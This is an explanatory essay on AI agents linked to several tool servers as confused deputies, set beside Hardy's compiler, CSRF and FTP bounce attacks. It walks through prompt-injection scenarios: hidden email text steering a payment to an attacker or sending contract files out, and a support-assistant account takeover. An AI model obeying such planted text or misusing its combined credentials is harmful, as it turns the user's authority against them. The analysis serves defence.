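# Agents Holding Many Servers' Credentials as Confused Deputies

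## Agents, tool servers and the credentials they hold

An AI agent is a language model that a host program runs in a loop. The model proposes an action, the program carries it out and returns the result, and the model proposes the next action. The model itself only produces text, so it can draft a reply to a supplier, but other software has to send it. Brooker, an Amazon Web Services engineer, points out in *Agent Safety is a Box* that running a model changes nothing in the world by itself. Agents use tools to pay, send and delete.

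Those tools come from tool servers, which are programs that offer agents a set of operations on some service, such as searching a mailbox, reading files or making payments. Many people connect several servers to one agent, which can then read a stranger's email through one and move money through another. This raises an old security problem called the confused deputy, in which someone misleads a program into using its authority for them when they lack that authority themselves. How well this description fits an agent depends on who holds which password and who reads what.

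The most widely used open protocol for connecting agents to tool servers is the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic released in November 2024. Soria Parra and Delimarsky, two of its lead maintainers, counted more than 700 million downloads of its developer kits in the 30 days to 23 November 2026, up from more than 90 million in November 2025 (*Two Years of MCP Builders*, 2026). Downloads are a loose measure of use because automated builds fetch the same package repeatedly. Tool calls are a closer measure, and by August 2026 ChatGPT users were triggering 98 times as many MCP tool calls as in January, according to the Agentic AI Foundation's *MCP Usage Surged as the Protocol Went Stateless* (2026).

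### One tool call from start to finish

Suppose a user has connected an agent to three servers, for mail, files and payments, and types: "Pay this month's invoice from the paper supplier."

MCP splits the work among three kinds of software. The host is the application in front of the user, for example Claude Desktop or Visual Studio Code; it runs the loop and keeps the conversation. Inside the host sits one client for each server, a component that talks to that server and no other. The servers may run on the user's own machine (local servers) or somewhere on the internet (remote servers). The call then goes like this:

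1. Before the user types anything, the host sends each server a `tools/list` request. Each server replies with its tools, giving for each a name, a description in ordinary English and the arguments it takes. The Model Context Protocol documentation has the host merge all the replies into a single registry.
2. The host gives the model the user's request along with the tool descriptions.
3. The model outputs a proposed call, which is a short piece of structured text: the name of a tool, say `search_mail`, and its arguments, here the supplier's name.
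4. The host looks up which server offers that tool, perhaps asks the user to approve, and has the matching client send the server a `tools/call` message.
5. The mail server turns the message into a request to the mail provider, adds a credential that the provider accepts, and gets the email back.
6. The server returns the email as text. The host appends it to the conversation and runs the model again, which can now read the invoice and propose a call to the payment server.

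The approval in step 4 is optional in practice. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification on tool calls, states that a human "should" always be able to refuse a call, and in the specification's language "should" is weaker than "must". The `tools/call` message contains the tool's name, the arguments, and some details of the client software and protocol version. It has no field identifying the text that led the model to propose the call, so the payment server can't distinguish a payment the user wanted from one that an email suggested.

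### One context for every server

A model's context is the text it receives each time it runs. The invoice agent's context contains one sentence from the user and a great deal of text that other people wrote. The developers of the three servers wrote the tool descriptions, and the supplier, or someone posing as the supplier, wrote the email. The context also includes error messages, because the model can often correct a failed call if it sees what went wrong. Since November 2026, servers have also been able to publish "skills", written guidance for longer jobs that Claude loads into its context when needed, according to Anthropic's *MCP servers can now ship skills, run tasks, and more with Claude* (2026).

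Under Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into other servers, and the full history stays with the host. But the host combines the context from all its clients. The supplier's email may appear a few lines below the description of the payment tool in the model's context, and the model processes both as one stream of text. Text from the mail server can therefore change what the agent does with the payment server, even though the two servers never exchange a message. The specification makes the host responsible for controlling such interactions but does not specify how, and MCP as a whole does not dictate how applications manage the context they gather.

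A single ordinary request can bring data from many sources into an agent's context. The Agentic AI Foundation gives the example of asking ChatGPT to help prepare for a meeting, which may require it to call a calendar, Slack, email and Google Drive. Outsiders can usually write to at least two of those, by sending an email or a calendar invitation.

Users do not always choose the servers their agent connects to. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) describes a feature that lets an administrator authorize a server once for a whole organization, after which employees have it from their first login. An employee may therefore type a request without having thought about everything the agent can reach. An agent's combined authority is everything its connected servers, taken together, let it do.

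### Permission, authority and tokens

In access control, a principal is the person or program whose right to do something is in question. A permission is a rule that lets a principal perform some operation on some resource. Brooker gives an example for a customer-service agent, in which a user named "refund-agent" (the principal) may issue a refund (the operation) through the refund gateway (the resource) only if the amount is under 500.

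An access control list is a common way to store permissions. It belongs to a resource, a shared folder for instance, and names the principals who may use that resource and what each may do. (The main alternative is a capability, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and permits its use.)

Authority is wider than permission because it covers everything a program can cause to happen, directly or through others, with the permissions it can use. For example, an agent may have permission to edit a spreadsheet of suppliers' bank details but not to make payments. If the accounting software reads that spreadsheet every night and pays the accounts listed there, the agent has authority over where the money goes, which an audit of its permissions at the bank would not reveal.

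Applications usually show remote services that they have permission by presenting an OAuth access token. OAuth is the standard behind the screens where users approve an application's access to, for example, their calendar. The user signs in at an authorization server and agrees to the access. The server then issues a token, a string of characters that the application sends with each request. MCP uses bearer tokens, which work for anyone who presents them.

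A token's scope and audience limit how it can be used. Its scope is the set of operations it covers, often with a label such as `files:read`. Its audience is the server it is meant for, and under MCP's rules any other server must reject it. In a walk-through of a single authorized request, *The Anatomy of MCP Authorization* (Dissanayaka, 2026) explains that the user still owns the files and the agent acts with authority borrowed from the user.

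### Where the credentials sit

A credential is any secret or token that a service accepts as proof of permission. The invoice agent depends on several, which may be stored in different places.

If the mail server is local and communicates with the host over standard input and output, it should take its credentials from the environment, the settings that the operating system gives a program when it starts (Model Context Protocol, *Authorization*, 2026). In practice, the user often pastes an API key, a long password for software, into a configuration file. Such keys can grant broad access. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026) describes a server for the code-hosting site GitHub that uses one key to reach every repository the key permits, including private ones, even when the user's request concerns a single public project.

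The host's client holds an OAuth token for the file server, which is remote, and attaches the token to every request. A host with ten remote servers manages ten such tokens. Jones (2026) notes in *MCP Is Growing Up* that this one-to-many arrangement requires attention to details that simpler applications can overlook, such as keeping each credential tied to the authorization server that issued it.

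The payment server is also remote, so the host holds a token for it. The payment server needs its own credential to log in to the bank. Dissanayaka stresses that a server must not forward the caller's token to the service behind it. The protocol does not cover what the server uses instead; Stack Overflow's *Is that allowed?* (2026) lists a username and password, an API key or another OAuth token. Often the credential belongs to a service account, which is set up for a program rather than a person. The bank then sees the same principal, the payment server, whichever customer's agent made the request. The payment server therefore has to check who asked and whether that person may pay from the bank account involved.

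Many servers don't check callers' credentials. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (2026) covers 7,973 remote servers, of which 40.55% let anyone call their tools without a credential, 29% relied on fixed tokens or API keys, and 30.45% used OAuth. *Exposed by Design* (2026), an audit of servers reachable from the internet, found a larger share without OAuth, 380 of 414. The difference probably reflects how each team found its servers. Missing authentication is harmless on a server that reports the weather, but it matters a lot when the server holds a powerful credential of its own or can run commands on its machine. The audit found 687 tools that could run such commands and required no credential.

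### Using a credential without seeing it

In the invoice example, the model produced a tool name and some arguments, and other software then added the credential, which the model never received. This is the usual arrangement, and some systems enforce it strictly. The hosted agent service described in Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* keeps OAuth tokens in a vault. When the model proposes an MCP call, the call goes to a proxy along with a token that identifies only the session. The proxy fetches the real credential from the vault and contacts the outside service, so even the program running the agent loop never has the credential.

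Anthropic built it this way because an earlier design ran model-written code in the same container (an isolated environment for running software) as the credentials. An attacker who could influence the model could steal the credentials just by getting it to read its own environment, then use them to open new sessions and give those sessions work. Agents that can run commands on a user's laptop often have a similar weakness, since those commands may be able to read files that contain local servers' keys.

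Hiding a credential from the model prevents theft, which matters because a stolen token works from anywhere, without the agent, until it expires or someone revokes it. Hiding it does much less to prevent misuse. The proxy attaches the payment token to any payment call the model proposes, and the payment server accepts any call within the token's scope, so the model can still cause a payment to the wrong account without seeing the token.

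Here, an agent "holds" a credential if calls it proposes go out with that credential, whether or not the model could reproduce it. The invoice agent holds its mail, file and payment credentials all at once, so it still holds the payment credential while reading a stranger's email.

### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text in material the agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction from its user. The email with the supplier's invoice might contain a request, in white text on a white background, to send the contents of the contracts folder to an outside address. The attacker has no access to the agent, the folder or the mailbox, but can still obtain the files if the model reads the message and follows the request.

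David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (UK National Cyber Security Centre, December 2025) explains why prompt injection is hard to fix by comparing it with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Programmers can reliably prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the user's input to the database separately, so that the database never treats the input as a command. A language model has no such separate channel. It receives its whole input as one sequence of tokens (words and pieces of words) and predicts the next token from that sequence.

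Developers can mark which passages came from outside, train models to give the user's instructions priority, or scan for attacks. David C regards all of these as attempts to add a distinction between instructions and data to a technology that lacks one. These measures make an attack less likely to work but don't rule it out, and he thinks it quite possible that nothing will ever stop prompt injection as completely as separate inputs stopped SQL injection.

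The task makes a clean separation even harder. The user asked the agent to pay an invoice, and the email contains the amount, due date and account number, so the agent couldn't pay it if nothing in the email could affect its actions. It has to use the account number and ignore the line about the contracts folder, and it can tell them apart only by judging what the text means. A sentence such as "please note our new bank details" could be a genuine update or an attack in itself.

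## Hardy's compiler, the original confused deputy

The term "confused deputy" comes from an accident on a shared computer in about 1977. In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Norm Hardy sets the story at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers, and calls it nearly true, with inessential details changed. By 1988 Hardy worked at Key Logic, whose operating system KeyKOS was built around the remedy he recommends, so he had a product to promote. Readers can still check his argument without trusting the anecdote.

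### How Tymshare lost its billing file

The program was a compiler, which translates programmers' code into a form the machine can run. Tymshare's staff kept it in a directory called SYSX. A customer started it with a RUN command and could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler ran with the permissions of whoever started it, so it could write to the customer's files.

The staff had also changed the compiler to collect statistics on which language features people used. The compiler wrote these to (SYSX)STAT, meaning the file STAT in the directory SYSX, and that name was in the compiler's own code. To let it write there, the staff gave the compiler an extra permission called a "home files license", which allowed a program to write to files in the directory where it was stored.

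SYSX also contained (SYSX)BILL, the billing records. A customer learned that name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system in a request to open the file for writing. The operating system opened the file because the compiler had a home files license. The compiler then wrote debugging output over the billing records, which were lost.

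Every part of the system worked as designed. The compiler treated this file name like any other, and the operating system applied its rule correctly. In Hardy's view, the debugging code was correct until the staff granted the license. To notice the problem, the staff would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file, and even then it isn't clear what they should have changed.

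### Repairs that don't work

One could make the compiler check the file name before using it. Hardy considers three such checks:

- The compiler could refuse names in other people's directories. But customers have good reasons to send output to another directory.
- It could refuse names in SYSX. But the directory did not yet have that name when the programmers wrote this code, and some people had legitimate access to SYSX and might want output there.
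- It could refuse (SYSX)BILL in particular. But SYSX held other sensitive files, and the programmers would have to update the compiler whenever the staff added another.

The operating system's rules were no easier to fix. Each clause Hardy and his colleagues added to let programs open files in a new situation created security holes in programs that had been safe, and each restriction they added broke programs that had been working. The last time Hardy wrote out the conditions for a program to open a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

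A more promising idea is to narrow the license so that it covers only STAT. That would have saved the billing records, since the compiler did not need to write to BILL. But a customer could still name (SYSX)STAT as the debugging file and destroy the statistics, because the compiler does need permission to write that file. Hardy mentions this only in a parenthesis, and many retellings omit it by making the billing file the one the compiler is supposed to write. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) simplifies the story in this way and explains in a footnote that the point is the same. The original is still worth keeping because it shows both that the license was too broad and that the compiler could use even a narrow license for the wrong purpose.

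Hardy leaves it as an exercise to show that access control lists do not solve the problem. One way to do the exercise is to suppose that the compiler's own permission covers only STAT, that the customer's covers only the customer's files, and that the operating system can check either or both:

| Whose permission the system checks | Statistics to STAT | Debugging output to the customer's file | Debugging output to STAT |
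| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| The compiler's | Allowed | Refused | Allowed |
| The customer's | Refused | Allowed | Refused |
| Either is enough | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Both are necessary | Refused | Refused | Refused |
| What Tymshare needed | Allowed | Allowed | Refused |

No rule produces the last row. The operating system cannot distinguish writing statistics to STAT from writing debugging output to STAT, because the program, customer, file and operation are the same in both cases. A rule based only on those four things must allow both requests or refuse both, however many clauses it has. *ACLs don't*, a technical report from HP Labs, claims more generally that access lists cannot decide correctly when an interaction involves more than two principals, because the information they need is lost as requests pass from one program to the next.

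### Switching hats

Tymshare's repair put some of that missing information into the request. The staff added a system call (an operation that programs can request from the operating system) that let a program "switch hats" and choose which of its two authorities to use. The compiler could then open STAT under its home files license and the debugging file under the customer's authority. If the customer named (SYSX)BILL, the request failed, as it should.

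This worked for the compiler, but some applications soon turned out to need more than two authorities. For example, a program that combined files from two customers and kept its own log would need three. The system also protected things other than files, and the call did not apply to the mechanisms that protected them. Hardy reports that nobody saw an obvious way to generalize the call, and that the changes it required were spread across the system.

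Switching hats also requires the programmer to write code that tracks which file names came from the customer and puts on the matching hat each time, because the compiler still receives the debugging file as a bare name. A mistake in one line of that code brings back the original vulnerability.

### A name from one party and permission from another

Hardy argues that the compiler failed because it ran with authority from two sources and could not keep them apart. It was meant to use the customer's authority to write debugging output and the license to write statistics, but when it asked to open a file, it could not specify which one it was relying on.

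The attack worked because the system had one mechanism for telling the compiler which file to write (security researchers call this designation) and another for permitting it to write there. Tymshare's staff supplied both the name and the permission for the statistics file, and the customer supplied both for ordinary debugging output. In the attack, the customer supplied the name and the staff had supplied the permission, and the operating system combined them without recording where either came from. Miller and colleagues argue that access-list systems can hardly avoid this, because they necessarily convey designation and permission separately.

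They also call the kind of authority that the compiler had ambient authority, meaning authority that a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to a world with doors but no keys, in which a door opens by itself if it finds the person in front of it worthy. File permissions on Unix, the family of operating systems that Tymshare's resembled, are ambient in this sense. A program asks to open a file by name without presenting a credential, and the request succeeds or fails.

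The customer's authority was ambient too. When customers typed RUN, the compiler ran with all their permissions, although it needed to write only one or two files for them. A malicious compiler could have used those permissions to delete all their work. Hardy describes this abuse of the user's authority as the Trojan horse, the companion problem to the billing accident, where a user misused the compiler's authority.

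Giving programs keys helps, but how they use the keys still matters. Suppose the compiler holds one key from the staff and one from the customer. The attack fails if the compiler labels each key with its purpose and uses it for nothing else, but still succeeds if it tries every key until one works. Miller and colleagues conclude that removing ambient authority makes it possible to write a deputy that nobody can confuse, but does not guarantee it. They would also make the name and the permission inseparable.

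A capability does this, since it both names a resource and permits its use. It is also unforgeable, meaning a program cannot produce one by guessing or spelling out a name. The program must either receive the capability from another program that already has it or create the resource itself.

A Unix file descriptor is close to this. It is a small number that a program receives when it opens a file. The number is an index into a table that the operating system keeps for that program, and the table entry records which file it is and whether the program may read it, write it or both. A program that makes up the number 7 gets no access unless the operating system has already filled entry 7. Programs can also pass descriptors to one another. Miller and colleagues consider file descriptors nearly equivalent to capabilities.

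### The compiler with two capabilities

In Hardy's solution the compiler uses one capability from the staff and another from the customer. UT Austin's *The Confused Deputy*, a set of course slides, shows how to arrange this with file descriptors. A run of the compiler then goes as follows:

1. Tymshare's staff install the compiler and give it a capability to write to STAT.
2. A customer asks to compile a program and chooses a file for the debugging output. A small launcher program, which has the customer's authority and none of the compiler's, opens that file and gets a capability to it.
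3. The launcher starts the compiler and passes it the capability as the place for debugging output.
4. The compiler writes its statistics through the first capability and its debugging output through the second. It needs no file names, and the operating system has no access list to consult.

If the customer types (SYSX)BILL, the launcher tries to open the file, but the operating system denies access because the customer has no right to it. The compiler therefore never gets a capability to BILL. The customer could send the compiler the text "(SYSX)BILL" by another route, but this compiler has no operation that turns a name into an open file.

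Naming (SYSX)STAT fails in the same way, even though the compiler has a capability to that file. The customer can't put the compiler's capability into the request, because the customer doesn't have it. To ask for output to a file, a customer must hand over the permission to write there, so a customer can't express a request to write to a file without having that permission. This also handles the case that made name checks awkward, where a member of staff has legitimate access to a file in SYSX. The staff member can pass a capability to that file, and the compiler will send its debugging output there without any special rule.

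The capability design prevents what the Tymshare customer did, which was to point a program at a resource they could not use themselves. The compiler's programmers can still make mistakes, such as writing debugging output through the capability meant for statistics, and some confused-deputy attacks succeed even against programs that use capabilities correctly.

Hardy and his colleagues had feared that capabilities would fill most of the machine's storage. He reports that their capability systems were usually smaller than equivalent systems with access lists, because capabilities replaced so many special-purpose mechanisms. He gives no figures for this, and he is judging a system he helped develop. He also warns that when systems added capabilities on top of traditional mechanisms, the combined disadvantages sometimes outweighed the combined advantages.

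### The same fault in browsers and file servers

Cross-site request forgery is probably the most common confused-deputy attack today, and the deputy is the web browser. When someone logs in to a bank's website, the bank gives the browser a cookie, which the browser attaches to later requests to the bank. MDN's *Cross-site request forgery (CSRF)* describes how an attacker can exploit this if the same person then visits the attacker's page. The page can contain a hidden bank transfer form, already filled in with the amount and the attacker as recipient, and a script that submits it as soon as the page loads. The browser may attach the cookie, in which case the bank treats the request as the customer's and transfers the money. Zeller and Felten (2008), in *Cross-Site Request Forgeries*, found that this attack worked against customers of ING Direct, a large American savings bank, which later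 fixed the flaw. They trace the problem to websites authenticating the browser and not the user.

Waterken's *The Confused Deputy rides again!* compares the browser with Hardy's compiler. The browser acts for its user, with the user's cookies, and also for every website whose pages it displays. When an attacker's page supplies the bank's address, the browser sends the request with the authority of the user's login, and nothing in the request shows whether the user or the page asked for it.

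The classic defence is for the bank to put an unguessable secret in its own form and reject any request without it. The attacker's page can't supply the secret, so the cookie alone is no longer enough. Waterken describes this as a move from ambient to explicit authority. A newer defence leaves the cookie ambient and adds information about where the request came from. Valsorda (2025), in *Cross-Site Request Forgery*, recommends that sites check the Sec-Fetch-Site header, which all major browsers have used since 2023 to report whether a request came from the same site or another one. Browser makers also tried to withhold cookies from many cross-site requests by default, but that mostly failed because it broke too many sites, especially their login systems. The weakness is still common enough to rank third in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025).

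The FTP bounce attack is older and involves no password or cookie. FTP is a standard for copying files between machines. The client sends the server a PORT command with a network address, and the server connects to that address to deliver the data. The address is normally the client's own, but the standard lets the client name any machine. CERT/CC (1998), a centre that publishes warnings about software flaws, describes an attacker who connects to a company's public FTP server and names a machine behind the company's firewall. The attacker cannot reach that machine but the FTP server can, so the attacker borrows the authority that comes from the server's position in the network. Allman and Ostermann (1999), in *FTP Security Considerations*, add that an attacker can first upload a file of mail commands and then have the server send it to another machine's mail port, which may let the attacker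 forge email there.

Like the compiler's debugging option, the dangerous feature has a legitimate use, which is copying files directly from one server to another. A CERT/CC advisory first issued in 1997 offers no clear-cut solution, because the standard requires the behaviour that makes the attack possible. In the advisory, Microsoft describes a fix that makes its server accept only the client's own address, which also prevents direct transfers between servers. MITRE's *Unintended Proxy or Intermediary ('Confused Deputy')*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, defines the general fault as failing to preserve the original source of a request before forwarding it. In the FTP attack, the machine behind the firewall receives a connection from the company's own server and cannot detect that an outsider requested it.

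## How an agent with many servers becomes a confused deputy

The payment server in the invoice example is in much the same position as the machine behind that firewall, since it cannot tell whether the user or a stranger prompted a call. What a stranger can gain from this depends on what the agent can do, which is a good deal more than pay one invoice:

| Server | Permission | What this task needs |
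| --- | --- | --- |
| Mail | Read mail | The supplier's invoice email |
| Mail | Send mail | Nothing |
| Files | Read files | Nothing |
| Files | Write files | Nothing |
| Payments | Read past payments | Nothing |
| Payments | Create payments | One payment to the supplier, for the amount due |

The task needs two of the six permissions, and only a small part of each: one message out of a whole mailbox, and one payment out of all those the bank balance would cover. (A careful agent might also read past payments to compare the account number with last month's, so the shortest list of permissions isn't automatically the safest.)

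### Two bad endings

Suppose the email with the invoice also contains planted text. In one version, the text gives the attacker's bank account as the supplier's. In another, it asks for documents from the user's contracts folder. If the model follows the text, the steps go like this:

| Step | Authority used | Who chose the details |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The email reaches the mailbox | The attacker's own ability to send email | The attacker |
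| The agent reads the email | The user's permission to read mail | The user, by asking for the invoice |
| *Wrong payment:* the agent pays the attacker's account | The user's permission to create payments, then the payment server's own login at the bank | The user asked for a payment; the attacker chose the account |
| *Stolen file:* the agent opens the contracts folder | The user's permission to read files | The attacker |
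| *Stolen file:* the agent emails the contents to an outside address | The user's permission to send mail | The attacker |

The attacker only has the authority to deliver the email to the mailbox. Every call the agent makes after that uses permissions the user gave it.

The theft uses the permissions to read files and send mail. Paying an invoice requires neither, so the user could have prevented the theft by switching them off. The wrong payment is harder to prevent because it uses the same two permissions the task requires. Preventing it requires a narrower payment permission, such as one limited to accounts the user has paid before, but that limit would also block the first payment to a new supplier.

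An agent can also make a payment the user never asked for. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli et al., 2026) describes a case where the user only wants a summary of the invoices in an inbox, but one message contains text requesting a payment. The agent passes this request to a finance agent without telling it that the task was read-only. The finance agent has a valid credential, so the payment goes through.

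### Why risk grows faster than the number of servers

If every server can both send and receive data, data from any of n servers can flow to the n − 1 others, which gives n(n − 1) one-way flows. Three servers allow 6 flows and ten allow 90. An eleventh would add 20 more, one in each direction between it and each of the other ten.

The wrong payment uses one flow, from mail to payments. The theft uses two, because the attacker's request goes from mail to files and the documents then go from files back to mail.

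This count of opportunities is a poor guide to how likely an attack is. Some servers make poor sources or destinations. For example, a calculator neither brings in strangers' text nor sends anything out. The formula also leaves out flows within one server. An agent with only a mail server can still read a malicious email and forward the rest of the mailbox to the attacker.

Still, checking servers one at a time misses most of the danger. *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025) examined 1,360 MCP servers for three kinds of tool that an attacker could chain together to steal data. It found 121 servers with tools that take in outside content, 149 with tools that reach private data and 89 with tools that send data over a network. Only two servers had all three kinds, but a user can easily combine them by connecting separate servers. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, tells users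 to avoid this combination. *MCPHunt* (2026), a test framework for agents with several servers, found that data crossed between servers in violation of policy with all five models it tested.

### How well Hardy's story fits

The agent corresponds to the compiler, its credentials to the home files license, and the attacker's account number to the file name (SYSX)BILL. The payment server, like Tymshare's operating system, checks only that the caller has permission. In both cases, the fault is that the system combines a name supplied by one party with permission supplied by another.

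The roles of the people involved match less closely. Tymshare's customer both started the compiler and attacked it, whereas in the invoice example the user starts the agent and someone else attacks it through an email. The compiler got its dangerous permission from Tymshare's staff, while the agent got its permission from the user, who is the victim. Cross-site request forgery is a closer match, because an outsider's web page directs a browser that carries the user's login.

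Surapani and colleagues list three differences from the operating-system case:

- The model's decision depends on the wording of its context and on chance. The compiler would have overwritten BILL every time, whereas the same email may fool an agent on one run and fail on the next. A successful test therefore proves less.
- Authority is spread over users, the companies that deploy agents, the agents themselves and outside services. The compiler had two sources of authority on one machine.
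- The malicious request arrives as content in a document or email. Hardy's customer filled in a field that was meant for a file name.

The attacker also needs to know less. Hardy's customer had to learn the exact name of the billing file. As *Silent Egress* (2026) points out, someone attacking an agent can describe the goal in ordinary language without knowing which tools exist or what arguments they take. The model works out those details.

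*Silent Egress* also describes an agent as confused about what its principal intended, whereas a traditional deputy is confused about which principal it is serving. The wrong payment fits this description, since the agent has one user and is trying to pay that user's bill, but is mistaken about which account the user meant.

### A formal definition

Gallo (2026), in *Proof-of-Continuity*, defines a confused deputy precisely enough to test it on agents. A privilege is a pair (o, r), meaning permission to perform operation o on resource r, and Priv(p) is the set of privileges that principal p has. A confused deputy occurs when there are a requester U, a deputy D and a privilege (o, r) such that:

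1. (o, r) ∉ Priv(U), so the requester lacks the privilege;
2. (o, r) ∈ Priv(D), so the deputy has it;
3. U sends D a request; and
4. D performs o on r as a consequence of that request.

In Hardy's story, o is writing and r is the billing file. But these conditions also cover things nobody objects to. Every customer who ran the compiler made it write to STAT, which customers could not do themselves, and Tymshare wanted this. Similarly, a payment company moves money between banks for shoppers who can't do it themselves.

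Gallo therefore also requires that the request pick out the target and that the requester not have been entitled to cause the action. Writing statistics to STAT no longer counts, because the customer did not choose that file. The shop payment doesn't count because the shopper was entitled to cause it. Overwriting BILL still counts. The refined definition is better, but it depends on someone deciding what each requester is entitled to cause, and Gallo takes those entitlements as given.

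### A user with less permission than the agent

The definition applies most directly when an agent has a powerful service account and takes requests from people with fewer rights. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He et al., 2026) gives the example of an employee who asks an agent for everyone's salaries. The employee cannot access the personnel database, but the agent can because it does administrative work. If the agent runs the query, all four conditions hold. A tool server can similarly become a confused deputy if it forwards requests to another service under its own identity.

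Something like this happened at Meta in 2026. Attackers asked the company's AI support assistant to link their own email addresses to other people's Instagram accounts, then had it send password-reset links to those addresses. The Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) report that the breach affected 20,225 people, began on 17 April and was discovered on 31 May. The attack worked only on accounts without two-factor authentication, according to this week in security's *Meta confirms thousands of Instagram accounts were hacked* (2026). Meta said that the assistant had functioned as intended and that a bug elsewhere had skipped the check that the email address belonged to the account.

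The attackers got the accounts by asking, without hiding instructions in a document. An ordinary web form connected to the same faulty code would probably have given them the same accounts. Stack Overflow's *AI agents are a confused deputy with the keys to your kingdom* (2026) argues that a more capable model would not have helped. It proposes that the function for changing a recovery address should take the requester's identity from the login session and refuse anyone who does not own the account, so that nothing an attacker types in the chat can change the result of the check.

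### An outsider whose text the agent reads

The invoice example does not fit the definition if U is the user. The user is allowed to create payments, read the contracts and send email, so the first condition fails for every step of both bad outcomes.

The conditions hold if U is instead the author of the planted text, and writing the email counts as sending a request. The attacker can't pay from the user's account, but the agent can, and the email causes it to. Other writers describe the attack in similar terms. text/plain's *AI Injection Attacks* (2025), by a browser-security engineer, warns that whoever wrote the web content an agent reads may take control of the agent. Surapani and colleagues describe outside content as borrowing the user's authority.

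But an honest supplier meets the same four conditions. It can't pay from the user's account either, and its invoice also causes the agent to make a payment. The user's request, however, entitled the real supplier to cause one payment of the amount due. In the usual setup, no credential or tool call records that entitlement.

Gallo handles the case differently, keeping the user as the requester but counting only the privileges the user selected for this task. If the user asks for a summary of a document, planted text in the document cannot properly lead to deleting files, even though the user is allowed to delete files at other times. This rules out the theft in the invoice example. It also rules out the wrong payment if the system describes resources finely enough, for example as "pay this supplier's existing account" rather than "create payments", which would cover the attacker's account.

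Siu and colleagues run into the same difficulty. They don't want to forbid every outside instruction, since a user who asks an agent to follow a recipe wants it to obey "bake at 350°F". They then imagine a recipe page with instructions for a shopping agent on which of the user's payment methods to use. They call this a security violation even though buying the ingredients serves the user's task. Yet their final formula allows an outside instruction whenever the resulting action serves the task, so it would allow this one. A rule based only on whether the action serves the task may miss a changed account number on an invoice for the same reason.

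Authors disagree about which of these situations to call a confused deputy. Siu and colleagues reserve the term for cases where a logged-in user has less permission than the agent, and define indirect prompt injection separately. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) uses it for cases where injected content turns an agent toward an attacker's goal. Gallo's definition can cover both, but the two cases need different repairs. Running the agent with each user's own credentials would stop the salary request, but it would not prevent the wrong payment or the theft in the invoice case, because the user's credentials permit both. SC Media's *After the identity fix* (2026) makes the general point that identity checks establish who is making a request, but not whether anyone asked for it.

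### The "inherently confusable deputy"

David C, writing for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, prefers to treat prompt injection as a confused-deputy problem. Developers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, as Hardy did by giving the compiler two capabilities, but David C calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy" because he thinks no fix will remove the risk that text misleads it.

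He therefore advises designers to assume that an attacker who gets text into the model's input can use its tools directly, and to ask how bad the result could be. They should limit the agent's actions with conventional software that does not rely on the model's judgement. They should also log failed tool calls, since an attacker will probably need several attempts. If the remaining risk is too high, a language model may be the wrong technology for the job.

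David C also recommends that when a model processes text from some party, its privileges drop to that party's. The rule comes from an online discussion between Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about prompt injection, and Baibhav Bista. It would prevent both bad outcomes, but it would also prevent the task, because an agent that had read the supplier's email could do only what the supplier can do, and the supplier can't pay from the user's account. Either the user would have to approve the payment, or software that had not been exposed to the email would have to make it. The Record's *UK intelligence warns AI 'prompt injection' attacks might never go away* reports that a participant in the same discussion acknowledged that the approach would "massively limit" what agents can do.

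Others who use the comparison are more hopeful. A post on the blog tianpan.co (2026) says that operating systems largely solved this problem decades ago and that developers can reuse the solutions. It says they should restrict which privileges outside text can command, instead of relying on filters that attackers can evade by rephrasing. This is right about the theft, which needs permissions the task never required, but too optimistic about the wrong payment, because the agent must have some permission to pay and must get the payment details from somewhere.

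### Prompt injection under an older name

One can also see all this as ordinary prompt injection, in which case the term "confused deputy" adds little. The two terms have overlapped for years. Willison (2023) wrote in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* that "confused deputy" describes the most dangerous form of prompt injection. In *The “S” in MCP Stands for Security*, a researcher from the security company Invariant Labs, posting as lbeurerkellner, called the problem with MCP "a special form of indirect prompt injection". On this view, isolating the servers from one another doesn't address the problem, because their tool descriptions all enter one context.

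If the fault lies in how the model reads text, the natural remedies are detecting attacks, marking outside text and training the model, which have the real advantage that they can leave the agent's permissions alone. A model that reliably ignored planted instructions could keep all six permissions and still resist the request for the contracts. (It would not have helped Meta, whose attackers made their requests openly.)

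Detectors perform poorly when an attack looks like normal business. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) tested two detectors on 8,400 emails. The emails came in pairs with the same professional text except for one clause, which asserted authority in one version and was neutral in the other. On a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect, Prompt Guard scored 0.43 and Prompt Guard 2 scored 0.59. The detectors received only the emails, with no information about what the user had authorized, and better detectors with the same input would still lack that information.

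Low failure rates also offer less protection than they seem to, because attackers can try again. If each malicious email has a 2% chance of working and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of fifty works is 64% (1 − 0.98^50). Surapani and colleagues accept such failure rates for the quality of text but not for actions that nobody can undo. They recommend filters and training to reduce bad calls, and a separate authorization check on each remaining call. They add that limiting authority without tracking the influence of outside text addresses only part of the cause. For the invoice, the check would have to determine whether the account number came from the user's records or from the email.

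## What studies and incidents show about misuse across servers

The invoice attacks are hypothetical, but researchers have successfully carried out very similar ones in test setups and against released products. There is much less evidence of criminals using such attacks on real victims.

### How many servers an attacker could use

The largest count is in *Parasites in the Toolchain*, which covers 12,230 tools on 1,360 servers from two public directories and a list on GitHub. The researchers looked for tools that suited any of the three stages of a data theft (taking in outside text, collecting private data and disclosing it). A language model and three human reviewers picked 5,666 candidates from the tools' descriptions, and an agent then called the candidates to check whether they worked as described. This left 1,062 tools (8.7% of the total) on 370 servers (27.2% of the total).

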